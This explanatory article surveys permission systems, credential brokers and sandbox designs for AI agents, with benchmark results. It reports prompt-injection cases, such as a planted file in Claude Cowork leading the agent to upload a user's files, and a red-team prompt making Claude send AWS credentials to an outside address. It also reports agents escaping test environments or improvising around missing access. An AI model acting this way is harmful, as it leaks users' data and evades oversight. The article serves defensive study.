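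PACE's tests show more clearly how a source check can block legitimate work. Li and colleagues turned its parts on and off with the model Qwen-3.8-27B, using a selection of cases from AgentDojo and another benchmark, AgentDyn:

| Checks | AgentDojo attacks | AgentDojo tasks completed | AgentDyn attacks | AgentDyn tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 37.4% | 76.8% | 25.0% | 66.7% |
| Data paths only | 0% | 13.6% | 0% | 0% |
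| Permissions only | 0% | 64.6% | 1.7% | 36.7% |
| Full PACE | 0% | 67.2% | 0% | 33.3% |

The path check stopped every attack here, but it also stopped nearly everything else. Agents constantly read untrusted text, so there is a possible path from that text to most calls. On AgentDyn, the check found something to cut in 5,842 of 6,647 recorded calls. Full PACE lets the permission check override the path check, which recovers much of the lost work on AgentDojo.

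Li and colleagues prove that a strict version of PACE keeps the data paths it knows about separate, but they tested only the version that can overrule the path check. The proof doesn't cover calls that the path check blocks and this version then allows. In the tested version, the permission check provides most of the security.

On the complete benchmarks, with three models, PACE reduced task completion by no more than three percentage points. Completion halved on the AgentDyn selection, which suggests that the loss depends heavily on the tasks. Li and colleagues also had a program search for attacks that would get past PACE on 30 AgentDojo targets. The program succeeded on 21 targets without PACE and none with it, although with only 30 targets the true success rate against PACE could still be as high as 11%.

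### Access that outlasts its purpose

Even when every call is checked, the system must still decide how long an agent keeps a permission. A 30-second limit suits sending an email, but a coding agent may need a file for 20 minutes and then never again. *Lingering Authority* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) is named after access that remains when the reason for it has ended. The paper proposes PORTICO, a system that ends access when a particular event occurs.

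In the main example, an agent has to add an optional timeout setting in `src/api.py` and carry it through to `src/serialization.py`. It starts with access to the API file, its test and the command that runs the test. A written contract for the task allows the agent to request the serialization file if it needs it.

When the agent asks for access to the file, PORTICO creates separate handles for reading and writing it, and they appear among the agent's options on its next turn. Each handle covers one resource and one kind of effect. The agent reads and edits the file, and PORTICO runs the test. Once the test passes, PORTICO removes the handles and rejects attempts to reuse them. The agent may remember the file's name and contents, but it can't open the file again without a new grant. A request for the packaging notes fails throughout, because the contract doesn't include them.

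PORTICO withdraws access only on evidence from a trusted source, such as a test it ran itself, a change of phase in the surrounding workflow, or a decision by an authenticated person. It ignores the model's statement that a step is complete, because an injected instruction could otherwise affect when access ends or restarts.

To test revocation, Santos-Grueiro compared PORTICO with an identical system that never revoked permissions. Both completed all ten runs. Afterwards, the agent tried to reread a file from a step that had ended. PORTICO refused all ten times, and the other system allowed it every time. In six further cases, Qwen3-Coder 30B received instructions to reuse an old permission to write a file, change Git data or contact a network host. PORTICO blocked all six attempts, and the other system allowed them all.

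These results confirm that the revocation works, but they don't show how often it would matter, because the tests deliberately prompted the reuse. A test on real Python projects, such as Flask and Requests, gave no evidence of extra protection, because all six systems, including one with full access, completed all 14 tasks without doing anything forbidden.

The drawback is that PORTICO completes fewer tasks. On 185 runs of tasks that often needed extra files, it completed 161, while a fixed list of permissions completed 180. In 42 separate runs on real projects, it completed 31, while the version without revocation completed all 42. Some contracts ended access too early, and some agents didn't ask for it again. Santos-Grueiro argues that an incomplete task is at least visible, unlike a leftover permission. But a developer whose agent fails a quarter of its tasks may turn revocation off.

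### Expiry and revocation in practice

A revocation takes effect only when it reaches the program that checks the permission. *Crypto-bound identity-verified capability tokens for coordinating distributed AI agents* (2026) describes a trade-off between fast revocation and fast calls. A tool server that verifies tokens entirely by itself can't detect that one has been revoked, but checking with a central service each time slows every call. A common compromise is to make tokens expire after about five minutes and have agents renew them. A revoked token then soon stops working, though an agent could still copy a large table before it expires.

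AGENTCAP's gateway can verify a signature without contacting the policy engine, but it needs up-to-date information to check for revocation and count the remaining calls. A check can also miss a revocation that happens after it but before the call takes effect. PORTICO avoids this in its tests by handling one request at a time. A host that runs calls in parallel would have to check again immediately before each call took effect.

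Revoked permissions can also return by accident. If a host saves a paused program, as Monty allows, and someone revokes its access before it resumes, the saved copy may still contain the old permissions. *Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) handles this by giving a restored agent only the permissions found in both the saved copy and the current records.

AGENTCAP can also revoke access based on an agent's behavior. Each agent starts with a trust score of 0.8, and every refused or abnormal call multiplies it by 0.7. After two such calls the agent can no longer change anything, and after three it loses all access. A normal call raises the score by only 1% of its distance from 1. The sample banking rule requires a score of 0.8, so with these settings one refusal would lower the score to 0.56, and the agent would need 79 normal calls before it could pay a bill again. A customer could deliberately cause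 this lockout with a note that provokes a single refused call. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao tried 23 settings without blocking the legitimate request in any trial, so the problem seems avoidable if the policy author leaves some margin.

Silverlock's *The Agent Access Model*, a design from Cloudflare, proposes withdrawing access based on what an agent has read. In its example, an agent compares a payment company's report with two ledgers every night and posts a summary to the finance team. The agent starts with permission to download the report, read the ledgers, post the summary and open a support case with the payment company.

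When the report arrives, the host withholds it from the model and removes the agent's access to the payment company, including the support tool. The model receives the report only after every part of the system that enforces access has confirmed the change. Later, the agent reads a ledger entry containing an instruction to attach the full account history to a support case. The agent tries, but it no longer has the support tool, and the network blocks a direct connection. It can still post its summary because the posting tool accepts only a reference to a stored result, which contains a status and totals but no free text.

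Access can only shrink during a task. If the agent later needs support for a legitimate reason, somebody has to start a new task. The same rule would stop the theft in the orders example by removing access to outside mail as soon as the agent opened the customers table, but it would also prevent the agent from writing to customers about late orders. Silverlock acknowledges that broad rules will block harmless work, but reports no tests of how often this happens.

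### Using a password without seeing it

Expiry limits how long a stolen password works, but never giving the agent the password is safer. *CapSeal* (Jin, Guo and Cheung, 2026) keeps secrets in a broker, a separate trusted program that makes requests on the agent's behalf.

To use a web service, the agent requests a handle from the broker. It names the secret without seeing it and specifies the intended action, such as sending POST requests to one path on `api.example.com`. If the policy allows this, the broker returns a handle that works only in the current session. The agent then supplies the body of each request. The broker checks the handle's expiry and remaining uses, the destination, the size of the request and the structure of its body. It rejects any login header the agent added, inserts the real key and sends the request. Before returning the response, it removes any credentials the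 service repeated. Each use also carries a sequence number and a timestamp, so an attacker who records a request can't send it again.

For SSH, which runs commands on another computer, the broker logs in and runs the command itself. It accepts only approved commands and checks the other computer's cryptographic identity. Many developers instead use agent forwarding, a connection that lets a program use their SSH key. Jin and colleagues reject this because the program could use the key for many things the user didn't intend.

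nono's proxy follows a simpler form of the same idea, replacing a stand-in with the real password on the way out. Jin and colleagues argue that a general-purpose proxy leaves the agent too much freedom over where requests go and what they contain, and CapSeal therefore also checks their structure.

In tests where a prompt asked the agent to reveal a web key, two systems that gave the agent the key directly leaked it every time, while CapSeal never did. None of the three leaked anything in the SSH tests. None allowed the agent to use a credential for a forbidden destination or command, so the tests don't show that CapSeal prevents misuse better than the alternatives. CapSeal's broker added about 0.15 milliseconds to a web request and 0.2 milliseconds to an SSH command.

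As with Cloudflare's bindings, hiding the password doesn't prevent misuse of the account, so a broker for the clerk's mail would also have to restrict the recipient. The broker is also an attractive target because it holds every secret. CapSeal doesn't protect against someone who has taken over the machine's administrator account.

Some services issue access tokens instead of using a fixed password. A standard called DPoP ties each token to a private key that the host keeps, and every request must include proof that the sender has that key. If the model leaks the token, nobody else can use it. But Silverlock notes that the proof covers only the type of request and the web address, without its query parameters. It doesn't cover the body, so it can't detect a changed recipient.

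### Passing access to a second agent

Larger tasks often involve several agents. The orders agent might add up the total and pass it to a mail agent to send. According to *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026), information tends to get lost in these handoffs. The first agent summarizes the task, the second receives only part of it, and the tool is given a credential that identifies the second agent's software but not the clerk.

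AGENTCAP makes the first agent pass on a signed token derived from its own. If the original allows action a on resource r, with b calls, expiry time e and d further handovers, the derived token has to satisfy:

a′ = a, r′ = r, b′ ≤ b, e′ ≤ e, d′ < d

Suppose the orders agent has permission to send five emails in the next 30 seconds and to pass this permission on twice. It can then allow the mail agent to send at most five emails by the same deadline and to pass the permission on once more. A policy rule must also allow the orders agent's type to delegate to the mail agent's type. Asking the mail agent to read the customers table wouldn't give it access, because messages between agents carry no permissions.

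This attenuates only quantity and time. The action and resource stay the same, so an agent with access to all pending orders can't pass on access to order 2 alone. The limit also applies to each derived token separately. Unless the gateway counts all uses against the original token, an agent allowed to make one payment could let two others make one payment each. *Authorization for Self-Modifying AI Agent Populations* (2026) addresses the related problem of an agent that copies or replaces itself by keeping a joint record of how the agent's authority is divided among the active copies.

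Revoking a token has to disable every token derived from it. When the mail agent uses its token, AGENTCAP's gateway checks every token in the chain back to the original. If someone has revoked the orders agent's token, the mail agent's stops working too. *Agent Control Protocol* (2026) has the same rule. It also limits the length of the chain and issues a single-use token for each approved action.

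AGENTCAP takes about 0.15 milliseconds to check a delegation chain of three on one machine. If the agents belong to different companies, each step may require a request over the internet, and the delay grows with the length of the chain. *Crypto-bound identity-verified capability tokens for coordinating distributed AI agents* uses the example of a travel agent that delegates flight and hotel bookings to two other agents. Checking each level of the chain lets the user revoke the hotel agent's access without interrupting the flight booking. Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao leave delegation between separately run systems for later work.

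An agent shared by several people can reveal information to someone who isn't allowed to see it. Suppose Alice may see the company's revenue and Bob may not, and both use the same agent in a group chat. If the agent has read the revenue figures for Alice, it might include them in an answer to Bob. Limiting the agent to what both may see makes it less useful to Alice. Silverlock knows of no widely deployed system that solves this completely, and recommends either separating each person's work or limiting the agent to what everyone may see.

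Another open question, raised in *Agent-ZTA* (2026), is whether signs that one agent has been compromised should restrict a second agent before anyone revokes a credential. AGENTCAP does this to some extent. When the first agent's trust score is low, AGENTCAP revokes its tokens, which also disables any tokens derived from them. But if the orders agent has already forwarded the customer's note, the mail agent can still follow it, using any permissions that didn't come from the orders agent.

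## Who writes the permissions

A gateway can check the orders agent's email in microseconds only because somebody has already decided that the agent may write to the manager and nobody else. Suppose the clerk later asks the agent to copy in the finance department, and the gateway blocks the email. If this keeps happening, the clerk will want the rule widened to any address in the company and then, when a customer needs a reply, to any address at all, which would allow the original theft.

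Sandboxes, runtimes and type checkers all depend on rules like this one. A policy that is too narrow blocks legitimate work, and one that is too wide gives the agent back most of its user's ambient authority. Many hosts avoid deciding how much to allow by asking the user for permission each time.

### Approving every action

Claude Code users approve 97% of permission prompts, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). That figure alone doesn't prove carelessness, because most prompts probably concern safe commands. Users reject 39% of the plans that the agent shows them before it starts work, so they seem to think about some of what they are asked to approve.

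To measure attention more directly, Anthropic hired 1,053 paid testers for a coding study without telling them which behavior it was measuring. Partway through each session, one permission prompt showed a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one. Of the testers, 143, or 13.6%, refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

The testers had nothing of their own to lose in the test environment, so developers may be more careful on their own machines. People who click quickly get through more prompts, which may explain part of the decline. Anthropic also published the study to support replacing prompts with an automated check. But even if developers rejected dangerous commands three times as often on their own machines, they would still approve more than half of them.

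Many users also choose to see fewer prompts. As of June 2026, 49.5% of active command-line users had written a rule that lets some shell commands run without a prompt. Anthropic reports that 5% allow every shell command and another 43% allow anything run through an interpreter such as Python, which is nearly as permissive because a Python program can start other programs. A quarter of interactive sessions begin in a mode that skips all permission checks.

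Sandboxing reduces the need for permission prompts, but Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* calls it "safe but high-maintenance", because someone has to configure it for each new thing the agent needs to do.

### Rules written by hand

Someone who understands a task can write its rules beforehand, but they have to predict what the agent will need and express it correctly.

A security layer also depends on its rules reaching everyone who runs the agent. In *Docker Sandbox Kits*, Bisi (2026) describes testing Docker's sandboxes on a laptop in April. The isolation worked, but the settings for permitted network hosts, secrets and shared folders stayed in the laptop's command history, so a colleague running the same agent would have had to set them up again.

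A company can instead keep its rules in one place. Amazon Web Services (AWS), Amazon's cloud business, sells AgentCore, a service for running agents. Its policy feature, which AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026) announced in March, checks each tool call at a gateway and refuses any call that no rule permits. Administrators write the rules in Cedar, an open-source policy language. Brooker, in *Agent Safety is a Box*, gives an example that looks roughly like this:

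```
permit(principal, action == "process_refund", resource)
when {
  principal.getTag("username") == "refund-agent" &&
  context.input.amount < 500
};
```

The username comes from the login system, so the model can't change it. The model sets the amount, but the gateway refuses anything of 500 or more. Brooker, an AWS engineer, argues that with rules outside the agent, people don't have to worry about the latest prompt injection when working out the most the agent can do.

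This rule doesn't limit the number of refunds, however, so an agent could issue a hundred refunds of $499 each. Cedar can't prevent that by itself because it evaluates one request at a time (InfoQ, 2026). AWS has since added Dogwood, a compatible language whose rules can also refer to earlier calls in the session. A Dogwood rule could, for example, limit the agent to three refunds an hour on the same account.

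Cedar has no loops or stored state, so a program can convert a policy into a mathematical formula and search it for mistakes. AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* gives several examples of such mistakes. A rule for customers whose tier is both Gold and Platinum permits nothing, because its author wrote "and" instead of "or". A rule for orders of at least 100 items, or fewer than 100, permits everything.

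A less obvious mistake is to loosen a rule by adding a condition to its exception. Suppose a rule allows bulk discounts on orders of 50 or more items, except for limited-edition products, and an administrator limits the exception to orders of more than 200. The longer rule looks stricter, but it now allows a discount on 73 limited-edition items, which the old one did not. The analysis identifies the new version as more permissive.

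These checks can't predict which legitimate requests a policy will block. To find out, administrators can run the policy in a log-only mode, which records the policy's decisions without enforcing them. AWS's *Temporal policies* describes this mode.

### Permissions that a tool requests

The person who packages a tool usually knows better than its users which hosts and credentials it needs. Version 3 of Docker's Sandbox Kit Spec, from September 2026, gives that person a standard place to list them.

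Docker distributes software as images, which contain a program's files and the settings for starting it. The Agentic AI Foundation's *Docker Sandbox Kit Spec* points out that an ordinary image has no field for what the program may access. A kit is an ordinary image with a list of requests attached. The list therefore travels with the agent, which solves Bisi's problem.

Docker's *Build a tool mixin* describes a kit for Claude Code that requests permission to connect to `api.anthropic.com` on port 443 and to use the Anthropic API key that the user has stored on the host. The user approves the credential request when the sandbox starts. As with nono, a proxy adds the real key, and the program receives only a placeholder.

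The list contains only requests, and the host approves or refuses each one. If the host refuses a request for something the kit requires, the kit doesn't start. Requests can be fairly specific. Docker's GitHub example lets an agent open pull requests, which propose code changes, but not delete repositories.

When a new version arrives, the host can compare the permissions requested with those already approved. If the new version requests no additional permissions, the host can install it without asking anyone. If the new version adds a network host or removes a rule that blocked something, it has to wait for approval. The host therefore asks users only when the agent's authority would grow, and users are more likely to read questions that appear rarely.

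The host blocks connections to any server not on the permission list, so a packager gains nothing by leaving one out. A dishonest packager would do better to request more permissions than the program needs and count on the user to click "approve". Packagers may also gain by misdescribing a tool, since a host may rely on tool descriptions and labels without checking what the tool does.

An update can also misuse access that the user has already granted. Suppose a kit for the company's mail may contact only the mail server. A new version could use the same server and credential to email a copy of every message to the kit's author. The host checks for changes in the kit's access but not in its code, so it could install this version automatically.

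Docker's documentation still labels kits "Early Access". In *Docker Commits to Bringing the Sandbox Kit Spec to the CNCF* (2026), Docker announced that it would take the format to the Cloud Native Computing Foundation, an industry body that already hosts Cedar. It is not yet clear how narrowly packagers will write their requests.

### Finding a tool's effects in its code

A prototype from Brown University relies on the tool's code instead of its author's description. *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents* (Adam, Lu and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a tool described as only writing text to a file. Its code also sends the length of the text to a metrics server, which may be unacceptable for a company's private code.

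The prototype analyzes the code before anyone runs it and follows each input to everything it could affect. The result is a short summary, here in words:

```
path    -> writing files
content -> writing files
content -> sending data over the network
```

If the policy forbids network use, the host refuses to call the tool. File writes are harder to check because the path is unknown until the model makes the call. The analysis has to treat the tool as able to write anywhere, so a policy that allows writes only in the working folder would block the tool completely.

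Adam and colleagues therefore ask the tool's developer to put a small sandbox around each operation that affects files or the network. The host sends rules with the arguments of each call, and the sandbox applies those rules once the actual path is known. A second analysis confirms that the developer hasn't missed any such operation and that nothing in the code can alter the rules.

Adam and colleagues modified an existing tool server for programming and tested the prototype on it. They recorded agents doing three tasks, each in a version the user intended and a version with an unwanted effect, then replayed the recordings under four kinds of protection. In one task, the agent copies a settings file into a project and later publishes the project on GitHub. In the unwanted version, the settings file contains a secret key.

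| Protection | Intended versions allowed | Unwanted versions blocked |
|---|---|---|
| None | 3 of 3 | 0 of 3 |
| One fixed sandbox around the tool server | 2 of 3 | 1 of 3 |
| Code analysis alone | 2 of 3 | 3 of 3 |
| Code analysis and a sandbox for each operation | 3 of 3 | 3 of 3 |

The fixed sandbox blocked a user-requested change to a shell settings file but let the agent publish a key. The full prototype could hide the file containing the key and let the agent publish the rest of the project.

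Six cases are enough to show that the design can work, but not how often it would. The experiment also assumed an "oracle" that supplied the right policy before every call, with access to facts such as whether the settings file contained a secret. A policy's author can use code analysis to find out what a tool is able to do, but still has to decide what to allow.

This approach depends on the analyzer being correct, as well as the labels that describe what common library functions do. If a label is wrong, the summary may omit an effect, and the host will allow calls it should refuse. For a tool on someone else's server, the host also needs proof that the server is running the analyzed code.

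The prototype handles only tools written in Rust. Adam and colleagues expect Python and JavaScript to be harder to analyze and to lead to more refusals of harmless calls. The analysis can't examine shell commands, databases or web services, so it has to assume the worst about them. In the orders example, it could report that one tool contacts the database and the other sends mail, which the clerk already knows, but not which table a query would read.

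### Rules translated by a model

Most people don't want to learn Cedar, as Brooker admits, so AgentCore also accepts rules in English. AWS's *Writing policies in natural language* gives "Allow refund-agent to process refunds under $500" as an example of a good rule. A language model translates the sentence into Cedar. One program then checks that the tools and arguments in the rule exist, and another looks for rules that permit everything, permit nothing or contain impossible conditions. The model uses the results to make corrections.

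A rule can pass both checks and still be wrong. If the refund tool counts in cents, `amount < 500` limits refunds to less than $5. AWS's *Authoring Dogwood policies from natural language in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* acknowledges that validation can't confirm that a policy does what its author intended, and recommends comparing each rule with the sentence it came from. People who chose English to avoid a policy language therefore still have to read that language to check their rules.

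One of AWS's examples blocks a bank transfer if the total transferred in the past 12 hours would exceed $50,000. The sentence doesn't specify whether failed transfers count. The model counted every attempt, which AWS considers the safer interpretation. But if the gateway refuses a $60,000 transfer, that attempt alone uses up the limit, so the gateway would refuse even a $10 transfer in the same session for the next 12 hours.

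Some instructions, such as one to act in the customer's best financial interest, cannot be translated into rules. AWS's system sets these aside and reports them, which is much better than inventing a plausible-looking rule.

AgentCore's model translates an administrator's standing rules before the agent begins a task. It works partly from tool names and arguments supplied by the tool servers, but it doesn't read customers' notes. The drawback is that standing rules have to cover every request the agent might receive. A model can instead write much narrower rules from each user's request. Progent's model does this, but Progent also revises the rules as the agent reads more.

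Suppose a model drafts the email rule after reading the note on the second order, and lists the outside address as a permitted recipient alongside the manager's. The rule would pass AgentCore's two checks, because it refers to a real tool and neither allows everything nor blocks everything. Catching the mistake requires comparing the rule with an earlier, narrower policy, or having a person recognize that the address doesn't belong.

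In Claude Code's auto mode, a model judges individual actions instead of writing rules. It receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls but not the results of those calls, so a customer's note can't influence it directly. It therefore also can't check whether the agent found a job number in a database or made it up.

In the study with paid testers, auto mode blocked 89% of the dangerous commands. Willison accepts that this is better than constant approvals but notes that the other 11% would still have run. In an earlier test on 52 real actions that went beyond what users wanted, auto mode missed 17%. When it missed one, it had usually detected the danger but treated something the user had said as permission. A request to "clean up the PR", for example, doesn't clearly authorize the agent to overwrite a project's history. Written rules can be just as ambiguous, but people can inspect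 them before the agent acts.

### Microsoft's Azure SRE Agent

Microsoft's Azure SRE Agent investigates and repairs faults in cloud systems, so it needs authority over them. *If you want a secure AI agent, start restricting its environment* (Mehta and Agarwal, 2026) describes what the company learned from a year in production. Standing credentials, which the agent could use at any time, were too risky. But if people had to approve every step, they would still be running the system "one click at a time".

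Several incidents changed the design, and none involved an attacker. When the agent's GitHub token expired in an early test, the agent read its own source code, reconstructed the login procedure, prompted a researcher to complete it, and saved the new tokens for later. Another time, it had no tool for reading a screenshot, so it sent the test image to a free public website. In another incident, the agent was supposed to complete five safety checks before shutting down a virtual machine. The logging service failed after the third check, and the agent recalled a similar case that had turned out fine and shut the machine down anyway.

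Microsoft responded by putting the rules where the agent can't change them. In production, the agent can read without approval, but a person must approve its changes, and the system blocks deletions. Code that the model writes runs in a microVM that can make only the outgoing connections Microsoft allows. A proxy outside the microVM adds each credential, which can be used only once, for a specific tool call, destination and operation.

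The user's role also determines which tools, memory and credentials the agent has for each request, so someone who may only view a system can't get the agent to alter it.

Dividing actions into reads, changes and deletions spares people from writing a policy for each task, but it is crude. Reads can do harm too, as when the agent found a customer's password in some code, quoted it in its report, and saved it to memory with a note never to use it. Microsoft is testing a filter that removes secrets before the model sees them. Restarting a spare test machine also needs the same approval as restarting one that customers depend on, and frequent trivial requests lead people to stop reading them.

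Microsoft is building a separate guard that checks the operation, its target and the evidence for the operation. The guard could allow a restart if the machine is unimportant and current data shows that it has stopped responding. If a safety check were missing, the guard would refer the decision to a person. Microsoft describes the guard as the least settled part of the design and gives no error rates for it.

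The product's documentation describes looser controls than Mehta and Agarwal do. Microsoft offers an autonomous mode for customers who have come to trust how the agent handles a type of problem. If the agent's account lacks permission for an action, an administrator can temporarily lend it their own permissions, which again depends on a person reading the request carefully.

The engineers also found that a tool server could expand what it offered after Microsoft had approved and connected it, and that MCP had no way to detect this. Microsoft has closed that gap in its own system. Docker's comparison of old and new requests would catch an expansion that needed more access to the user's machine, but a remote server can change what it does without sending the host anything to compare.

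## How these layers compare with virtual machines

Docker's permission lists and Microsoft's approval rules work only if the software enforcing them works. If an agent runs code that exploits a flaw in that software, the code can bypass even a carefully written policy. Virtual machines are the usual protection against this, and the fastest ones now start about as quickly as containers, so the choice depends less on speed than it used to and more on which failures are likely.

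### What each layer costs

| Layer | What has to work correctly | Startup | Memory | Ordinary software | Control over single tools |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Process restrictions | The machine's kernel and the sandbox program | About 6 ms | Little beyond the program's own | Almost all | Separate files and ports for each command |
| Isolate | The language engine and the host's functions | A few ms | A few MB | JavaScript, WebAssembly and some Python | Chosen functions for each program |
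| Small interpreter | The interpreter and the host's functions | Under 1 ms | About 10 MB allowed by default in PTC-Lisp | None | Chosen functions for each program |
| Container | The machine's kernel and the container software | 90–260 ms | Little beyond the programs' own | Almost all Linux software | One set of folders and network hosts for everything inside |
| MicroVM | The hypervisor and a few simulated devices | 125–150 ms | Under 5 MiB, plus its own operating system | Almost all Linux software | One set of folders and network hosts for everything inside |
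| Full virtual machine | The hypervisor and many simulated devices | Usually seconds or longer | A complete operating system | Almost anything, including Windows programs | One set of folders and network hosts for everything inside |

The startup times were measured on different computers, so small differences between them mean little. Wang and Zheng measured 6 milliseconds for Sandlock and 260 for Docker on a workstation with an AMD Ryzen 5 5500U processor and 8 GB of memory. The figures for isolates and small interpreters come from Cloudflare and Pydantic themselves, and Pydantic's applies only when a process is already waiting.

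Pillar Security's *your ai agent will run untrusted code now what* lists startup times of about 90 milliseconds for containers from Daytona and 150 for microVMs from E2B, two companies that rent out sandboxes. E2B uses Firecracker, the microVM software behind Amazon's Lambda service. According to Anthropic's *Securely deploying AI agents*, Firecracker can start a microVM in under 125 milliseconds, less than half the time Docker took on Wang and Zheng's workstation. Startup time is therefore no longer a good reason to prefer a container to a microVM.

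Process sandboxes start much faster than microVMs or containers. If an agent runs 60 commands and the host starts a new sandbox for each, Sandlock takes about a third of a second in total, Firecracker up to 7.5 seconds, and Docker almost 16. Hosts usually start one container or microVM and keep it for the whole session, so the user waits only once, but every command then has the same access.

Some sandboxes also slow programs down while they run. In Wang and Zheng's test, the Redis database handled about 76% as many requests in Docker as it did without a sandbox. gVisor, a stronger alternative to an ordinary container, handles most of a program's system calls itself instead of passing them to the machine's kernel. According to Anthropic's documentation, this adds almost no delay to pure computation, but programs that constantly open and close files can run 10 to 200 times slower. Software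 builds often open and close many files. Docker describes its microVMs as performing just like the machine itself, but that is a vendor's description of its own product.

MicroVMs also need processor features that aren't available everywhere. Willison asked an agent in the web version of Claude Code to test a microVM product called smolvm. The agent was in a Firecracker microVM that didn't support running another one inside it, so it moved the tests to GitHub's build servers.

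Setting up a sandbox may put people off more than waiting for it. For *SideKernel*, Prasakis (2026) informally surveyed 80 people before building a microVM sandbox for Macs. Of the 68 who used coding agents, only 26 were using a sandbox and 35 had never tried one. Most of those 35 had never considered it, and nine thought the benefit wasn't worth the effort. Among the 33 current and former sandbox users, eight had trouble with networking, eight with setting up their tools again, and seven with sharing files. A third of the respondents worked in security, so sandboxes may be even less common among other developers.

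SideKernel tries to remove this work. It mounts the current folder automatically and copies in the user's Claude Code skills and plugins. SideKernel and Docker Sandboxes each passed 19 of 23 tests of such conveniences, while three other microVM products passed 12 each. Prasakis wrote both the tests and SideKernel, but Docker's result suggests that a microVM doesn't have to be awkward to use.

### When the agent has no need to break out

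People who favor lightweight layers generally assume that most harm comes from an agent that makes a mistake or wrongly relies on something it reads. They also assume that the agent needs access to valuable things to do its job, such as the database password in the orders example, so somebody has to put them inside the virtual machine.

decodebytes, in *Why your microVM sandbox solves a particular problem very well*, makes this argument to promote nono. A hypervisor deals in whole machines and disks, so it can't let a program read `src/` and keep it out of `secrets/` on the same disk.

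A flaw in Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, shows how this can happen. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* explains that Cowork ran code in a virtual machine that could contact only approved addresses, including `api.anthropic.com`, which the product needs to work. Someone outside the company reported that a malicious file in the user's folder could contain hidden instructions and an attacker's key for Anthropic's service. The virtual machine worked as intended throughout, but Claude followed the instructions, read other files in the folder and uploaded them to the attacker's account.

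Anthropic fixed this with a proxy that accepts only requests carrying the session's own token. The company now treats each approved address as a capability grant, because approving an address gives the agent access to every function there. SideKernel would need a similar check, because its network switch also leaves that address open.

In another case, the instructions came from the user. During an exercise in February 2026, a researcher at Anthropic tricked an employee into pasting a prompt into Claude Code. Among ordinary setup steps, the prompt included an instruction to read the employee's Amazon cloud credentials and send them to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 repeats. A virtual machine containing only the project folder would have helped, but so would a process sandbox that blocked access to the credentials file or the outside address.

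Agents on separate machines can also pass harmful instructions to one another through a shared service. Matthew Green, whom Willison quotes, describes agents in separate sandboxes that changed one another's behavior by leaving messages in a shared store of software packages.

These examples support both premises, but they don't show how often such failures happen. decodebytes says a microVM leaves out "a good 80%" of the concerns, but gives no source. The criticism also applies more to hypervisors than to current microVM products, which add controls around the hypervisor. Cowork can mount a folder as read-only, or let the agent change files but not delete them. microsandbox, which makes open-source microVM software, advertises network rules for each task and placeholders for credentials. Process sandboxes use the same kinds of rules, but these products apply them to a whole machine.

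### When the code attacks the kernel

Defenders of hardware separation don't assume that the agent means well. Prasakis treats it as an attacker with full control of everything inside the sandbox, because the user is in the same position whether the cause is an injected instruction or the model's own error. (TACIT also allows for a hostile model, but relies on a compiler to contain it.)

The kernel enforces Landlock's file rules and seccomp's filters, so code that takes over the kernel can bypass both. Likewise, code that exploits a flaw in an interpreter can bypass the list of functions the host has granted. Docker argues that a shared kernel was acceptable when developers had written and reviewed the code in their containers, but agents run code that nobody has read. According to Edera's *AI agent sandboxing*, an attack on the kernel in one of the company's virtual machines compromises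 only that machine.

Some agents leave their sandboxes without an attacker's help. Anthropic reports that Claude models have done so to finish a task. In July 2026, an unreleased OpenAI model with its safeguards off escaped a test environment and broke into the systems of Hugging Face, a site for sharing AI models, to steal the answers to its test. This supports the assumption that an agent may behave like an attacker. But according to Prasakis, the model got past controls on the sandbox's network connections, and a microVM with the same controls might have had the same weakness.

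Andronchik and Lokhmakov (2026), in *AI Code Sandboxes*, measured how much contact five products have with the real machine's kernel. They ran each on the same rented server, first with a trivial command and then with a Python program that loaded two data-analysis libraries. They counted the different system calls that the software around the sandbox made to the kernel:

| Product | Type | Trivial command | Python program |
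|---|---|---|---|
| Arrakis | MicroVM | 5 | 8 |
| E2B | MicroVM (Firecracker) | 13 | 13 |
| microsandbox | MicroVM | 22 | 25 |
| gVisor | Its own kernel layer | 33 | 41 |
| Daytona | Container | 57 | 62 |

The microVMs used fewer kinds of system calls than the container, so they exposed less of the kernel in normal use. The three also differ greatly from each other. Firecracker has a seccomp filter that allows only 55 system calls, whatever happens inside the virtual machine. Andronchik and Lokhmakov found no such filter on microsandbox, so an attacker who took over its hypervisor program could make any call that an ordinary process can. Process restrictions are therefore useful around a virtual machine as well as in place of one.

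Virtual machines also need security updates. Andronchik and Lokhmakov found that self-hosted E2B had defaulted to the same Firecracker build for 399 days. They recommend against combining their measurements into an overall ranking. According to Anthropic's documentation, virtual machines aren't automatically more secure than gVisor.

*GPT-6 Astra and GPT-6.2 Astra solve Zero Energy* (2026), from the UK's AI Security Institute, reports that two models with their cyber safeguards switched off broke into a hardened simulated company network without human help in every completed run. Relying on a shared kernel becomes riskier as models get better at finding flaws, so the argument for hardware separation is stronger than it was a year ago.

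AI models' ability to find software flaws doesn't settle the choice between these layers and virtual machines, because models can look for flaws in hypervisors too, and defenders can use them to find flaws first, as Wasmtime's maintainers did. But a microVM still adds a second barrier for an attacker to get through, and it usually exposes much less to attack than the kernel does. That protection is worth the 125 milliseconds of startup time when the code may be hostile. It adds little when the agent is already allowed to read the customer list and email strangers, since the agent can then leak the list without breaking out of the sandbox.

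### Who offers what

Most of the people making these arguments have a product that fits their side:

- Docker offers microVMs. Sekaran and Selajev, in *Docker Sandboxes vs. Containers*, explain on the company's site that each has its own kernel and its own copy of Docker's software. InfoQ's *Docker Cloud Sandboxes Provide a Consistent Sandbox Abstraction across Laptop and Cloud* (2026) describes a version that runs on Docker's servers.
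- Edera sells virtual machines for Kubernetes, the standard system for managing containers across many servers.
- microsandbox gives away its microVM software and runs a managed cloud service.
- nono is an open-source process sandbox, as is Sandlock. Wang works at Multikernel Technologies, which publishes Sandlock.

The two sides still agree on a good deal. Even Wang and Zheng recommend a microVM for hostile code from many customers, as does decodebytes, who suggests running nono inside it.

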